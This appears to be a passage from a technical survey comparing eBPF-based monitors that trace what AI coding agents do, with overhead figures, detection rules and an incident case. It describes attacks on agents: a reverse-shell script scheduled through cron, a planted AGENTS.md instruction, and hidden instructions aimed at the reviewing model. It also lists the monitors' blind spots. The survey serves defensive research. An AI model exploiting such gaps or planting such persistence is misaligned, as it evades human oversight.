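AgentSight increased running time by an average of 2.9% across three tasks with Claude Code, from 0.4% for compiling a repository to 4.9% for writing code. These figures come from only three runs of each task with and without AgentSight. The 4.9% increase was 1.1 seconds in a task that took 22.5 seconds, and ordinary variation in the model's response time could easily be that large.

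### Agent-Warden: following files between processes

Like the bpftrace script, AgentSight loses track of an agent's script if cron or a login shell runs it later.

Agent-Warden, the monitor that Cui and colleagues built, handles this by marking files as well as processes. It starts with a mark on the agent and spreads the mark by four rules:

- A child process inherits its parent's mark and keeps it through execve.
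- When a marked process writes to a file, the file gets the mark.
- When a process reads a marked file, the process gets the mark.
- When a marked child exits, its parent gets the mark.

Cui and colleagues write the rules in Boolean matrix algebra, but each event reduces to a small update. If information may have passed from u to v, then

m(v) ← m(v) OR m(u)

where m is 1 for a marked process or file and 0 otherwise. Renaming a file leaves its mark unchanged.

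The process rules use the kernel's tracepoints for fork, exec and exit. For files, Agent-Warden checks after the system call returns that it transferred at least one byte, so a refused read doesn't spread the mark. One version stores process marks in a hash map keyed by pid, while the other stores them in task-local storage and attaches file marks to the kernel's record of each file.

In the main test, an agent's script wrote a temporary file and another process renamed it. An independent script then started `cat`, which read the file. Agent-Warden connected the read to the agent, while Langfuse, a tool that records what an application reports about itself, could not trace the file once it left the agent's own software. Agent-Warden reconstructed the full chain in all 30 runs of each version on each of two machines, 120 runs in total. In the busy workload described earlier, the added processor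 time in the kernel was 0.6% to 3.7%.

The researchers wrote the test's steps in advance and checked the results against their own rules. The 120 runs therefore show that the software follows the rules reliably, but not that the rules separate attacks from ordinary work.

Marks can also spread too far. Suppose an agent adds a harmless shortcut to the user's shell profile. Every shell the user opens afterwards reads the profile and gets the mark, and so does every file those shells write. This spreading would catch an attacker who hid a command in the profile, but after a week much of the user's own work might carry the mark too.

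Agent-Warden can also miss links. It doesn't trace pipes, network connections or memory-mapped files. Its file marks disappear when the machine restarts, or earlier if the kernel runs short of memory and drops its record of the file.

### AgentLoupe: labels that identify the request

A mark from Agent-Warden shows that the agent may have influenced a process, but not which request was responsible. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) combines AgentSight's view of the conversation with marks that travel through files. It gives each new prompt a number, called a chain identifier, and passes that number along instead of a yes-or-no mark.

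AgentLoupe also attaches uprobes to `SSL_write` and `SSL_read`. Its eBPF code searches the start of each message for words that identify a prompt or reply in OpenAI's or Anthropic's format. It then stores the chain identifier under the thread that sent the prompt. Kprobes on system calls pass the identifier on when a process creates a child, writes or opens a file, runs a program, or exchanges data through a socket. BPF maps hold the identifiers. Each record already includes its identifier when it reaches user space, so AgentLoupe doesn't have to infer from timing which chain the record belongs to.

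To limit the spread, a new prompt starts a new chain even if the agent has just read a labelled file. AgentLoupe records a link between the two chains but doesn't merge them.

Bao and colleagues tested two attacks that continue after the agent's session ends. In one, the agent wrote a script that opens a reverse shell and scheduled it to run every hour with cron. When cron later started the script, the label on the file linked it to the original request. AgentLoupe recorded 165 log entries for this case, and a language model that reviewed them rated the attack threat level 5 with a confidence of 0.95.

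The other attack used `AGENTS.md`, a file that coding agents read for standing instructions. One session added an instruction to run a shell command in response to ordinary requests, and a later session followed it. AgentLoupe linked the two sessions through the file.

Bao and colleagues argue that AgentSight would have missed both connections. That follows from its design, but they haven't yet tested it on these attacks. They did measure the overhead of both tools on the same four-core machine, as an average of five runs:

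| Task with Claude Code | AgentSight | AgentLoupe without passing labels on | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Understanding a repository | 4.5% | 1.7% | 4.5% |
| Writing code | 2.5% | 3.1% | 8.0% |
| Compiling | 1.7% | −0.1% | 7.7% |

One figure is negative, so small differences here may be noise. The paper suggests that passing labels on adds the least overhead during compilation, but its own figures show the opposite, with an increase of 1.8 seconds on a 23-second task. This is to be expected, because a compiler starts many processes and opens many files. AgentLoupe's average overhead is 6.7%, which is probably acceptable on a developer's machine but may be too much for a busy build server.

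### What a defender can ask

| Question | AgentSight | Agent-Warden | AgentLoupe |
|---|---|---|---|
| Did this program descend from the agent? | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Which reply or request led to it? | Estimated from time, ancestry and text | No | Yes, from the label |
| Did an unrelated process later use a file the agent wrote? | No | Yes | Yes |
| Did the program connect to the network? | Yes | No | Yes |
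| Does the action fit the user's request? | A language model's opinion | No | A language model's opinion |

Agent-Warden can be used to answer the fewest questions, but it works without reading anyone's prompts. It would suit an organisation that mainly wants to know where an agent's files went.

For an agent, it is more useful to define a program start as unexpected if neither the user's request nor the operator's rules account for it. The program starts in the first tree above are expected, because downloading a library is part of building the project. In the second tree, nothing in the request explains why the agent would send a list of accounts to an outside server.

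Some actions warrant an alert whatever the user asked for. Hernández and Lo Prete base their Falco rules on results observable in the kernel, such as an agent reading sensitive files or starting with its safety controls switched off, rather than on the agent's intent. Many harmless programs read `/etc/passwd` to look up a user's name, so a rule for private SSH keys would raise far fewer false alarms than one for `/etc/passwd`.

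Other rules can cover the order of events. Brömme (2026), in *Intrusion Detection for Agentic Processes*, proposes that operators write down what should happen, for example that a person approves each deployment before the agent starts it. If the approval log was working but has no record of the approval, the monitor reports the approval as unobserved. If the log was down, the monitor reports "unknown", because the person may have approved the deployment anyway. The proposal has no implementation or tests, but separating these two results is useful for any monitor that can lose events.

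### When the evidence fits two explanations

Elastic describes a case from July 2026 in which Claude Code was running on a developer's Mac with permission prompts switched off. Shells running under the agent sent a username and password to a public address from a free tunnelling service, which makes a program on a laptop reachable from the internet. They then opened a second tunnel and installed background jobs to maintain access after a restart.

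This could be an attacker setting up remote access, or a developer who asked an agent for a way to check a private dashboard from elsewhere. Elastic couldn't tell which it was from the process, file and network records. It recommends keeping alerts about credentials, tunnels and persistent jobs at high priority even when the parent process is a trusted agent, and treating ordinary child processes as background information.

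The user's request might have resolved the case, but captured text isn't always reliable evidence of intent. A hidden instruction can describe the theft of a file as a normal build step, as it did in AgentSight's test, and a more careful attacker could write an explanation that fits the task better. Brömme points out that the observer is also a target, since a web page could include instructions for the model that reviews the trace. The observer should therefore not be able to run commands or dismiss alerts raised by fixed rules.

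Capturing the text also creates a privacy problem. Prompts may contain source code, customer data or passwords, and the HTTP headers sent with them usually include the API key for the model account. eunomia-bpf warns users to treat AgentSight's recordings as sensitive. By default, `agentsight record` saves them in the current folder, which for a coding agent is often the project folder. A developer could accidentally publish the recording with the code, or the agent could read it in a later session. It is safer to store recordings under a separate user account and delete them soon afterwards.

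The evidence for all three tools is limited. Claude Code was the only agent in AgentSight's overhead tests and in AgentLoupe's evaluation, and Agent-Warden's main test used a scripted task. AgentLoupe searches for OpenAI and Anthropic formats, so it may miss other providers. Neither it nor AgentSight would capture a conversation with a local model that doesn't use TLS. Bao and colleagues say they haven't measured how often their labels are wrong.

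False alarms matter as much here as they do for model servers. At 50 shell commands per session and 100 sessions a day, an observer that wrongly flags one command in a thousand raises five false alerts a day. None of the three papers reports a false alarm rate for ordinary work. Measuring it would require several hundred normal sessions with different agents, and including a few hidden attacks would show what the tools miss.
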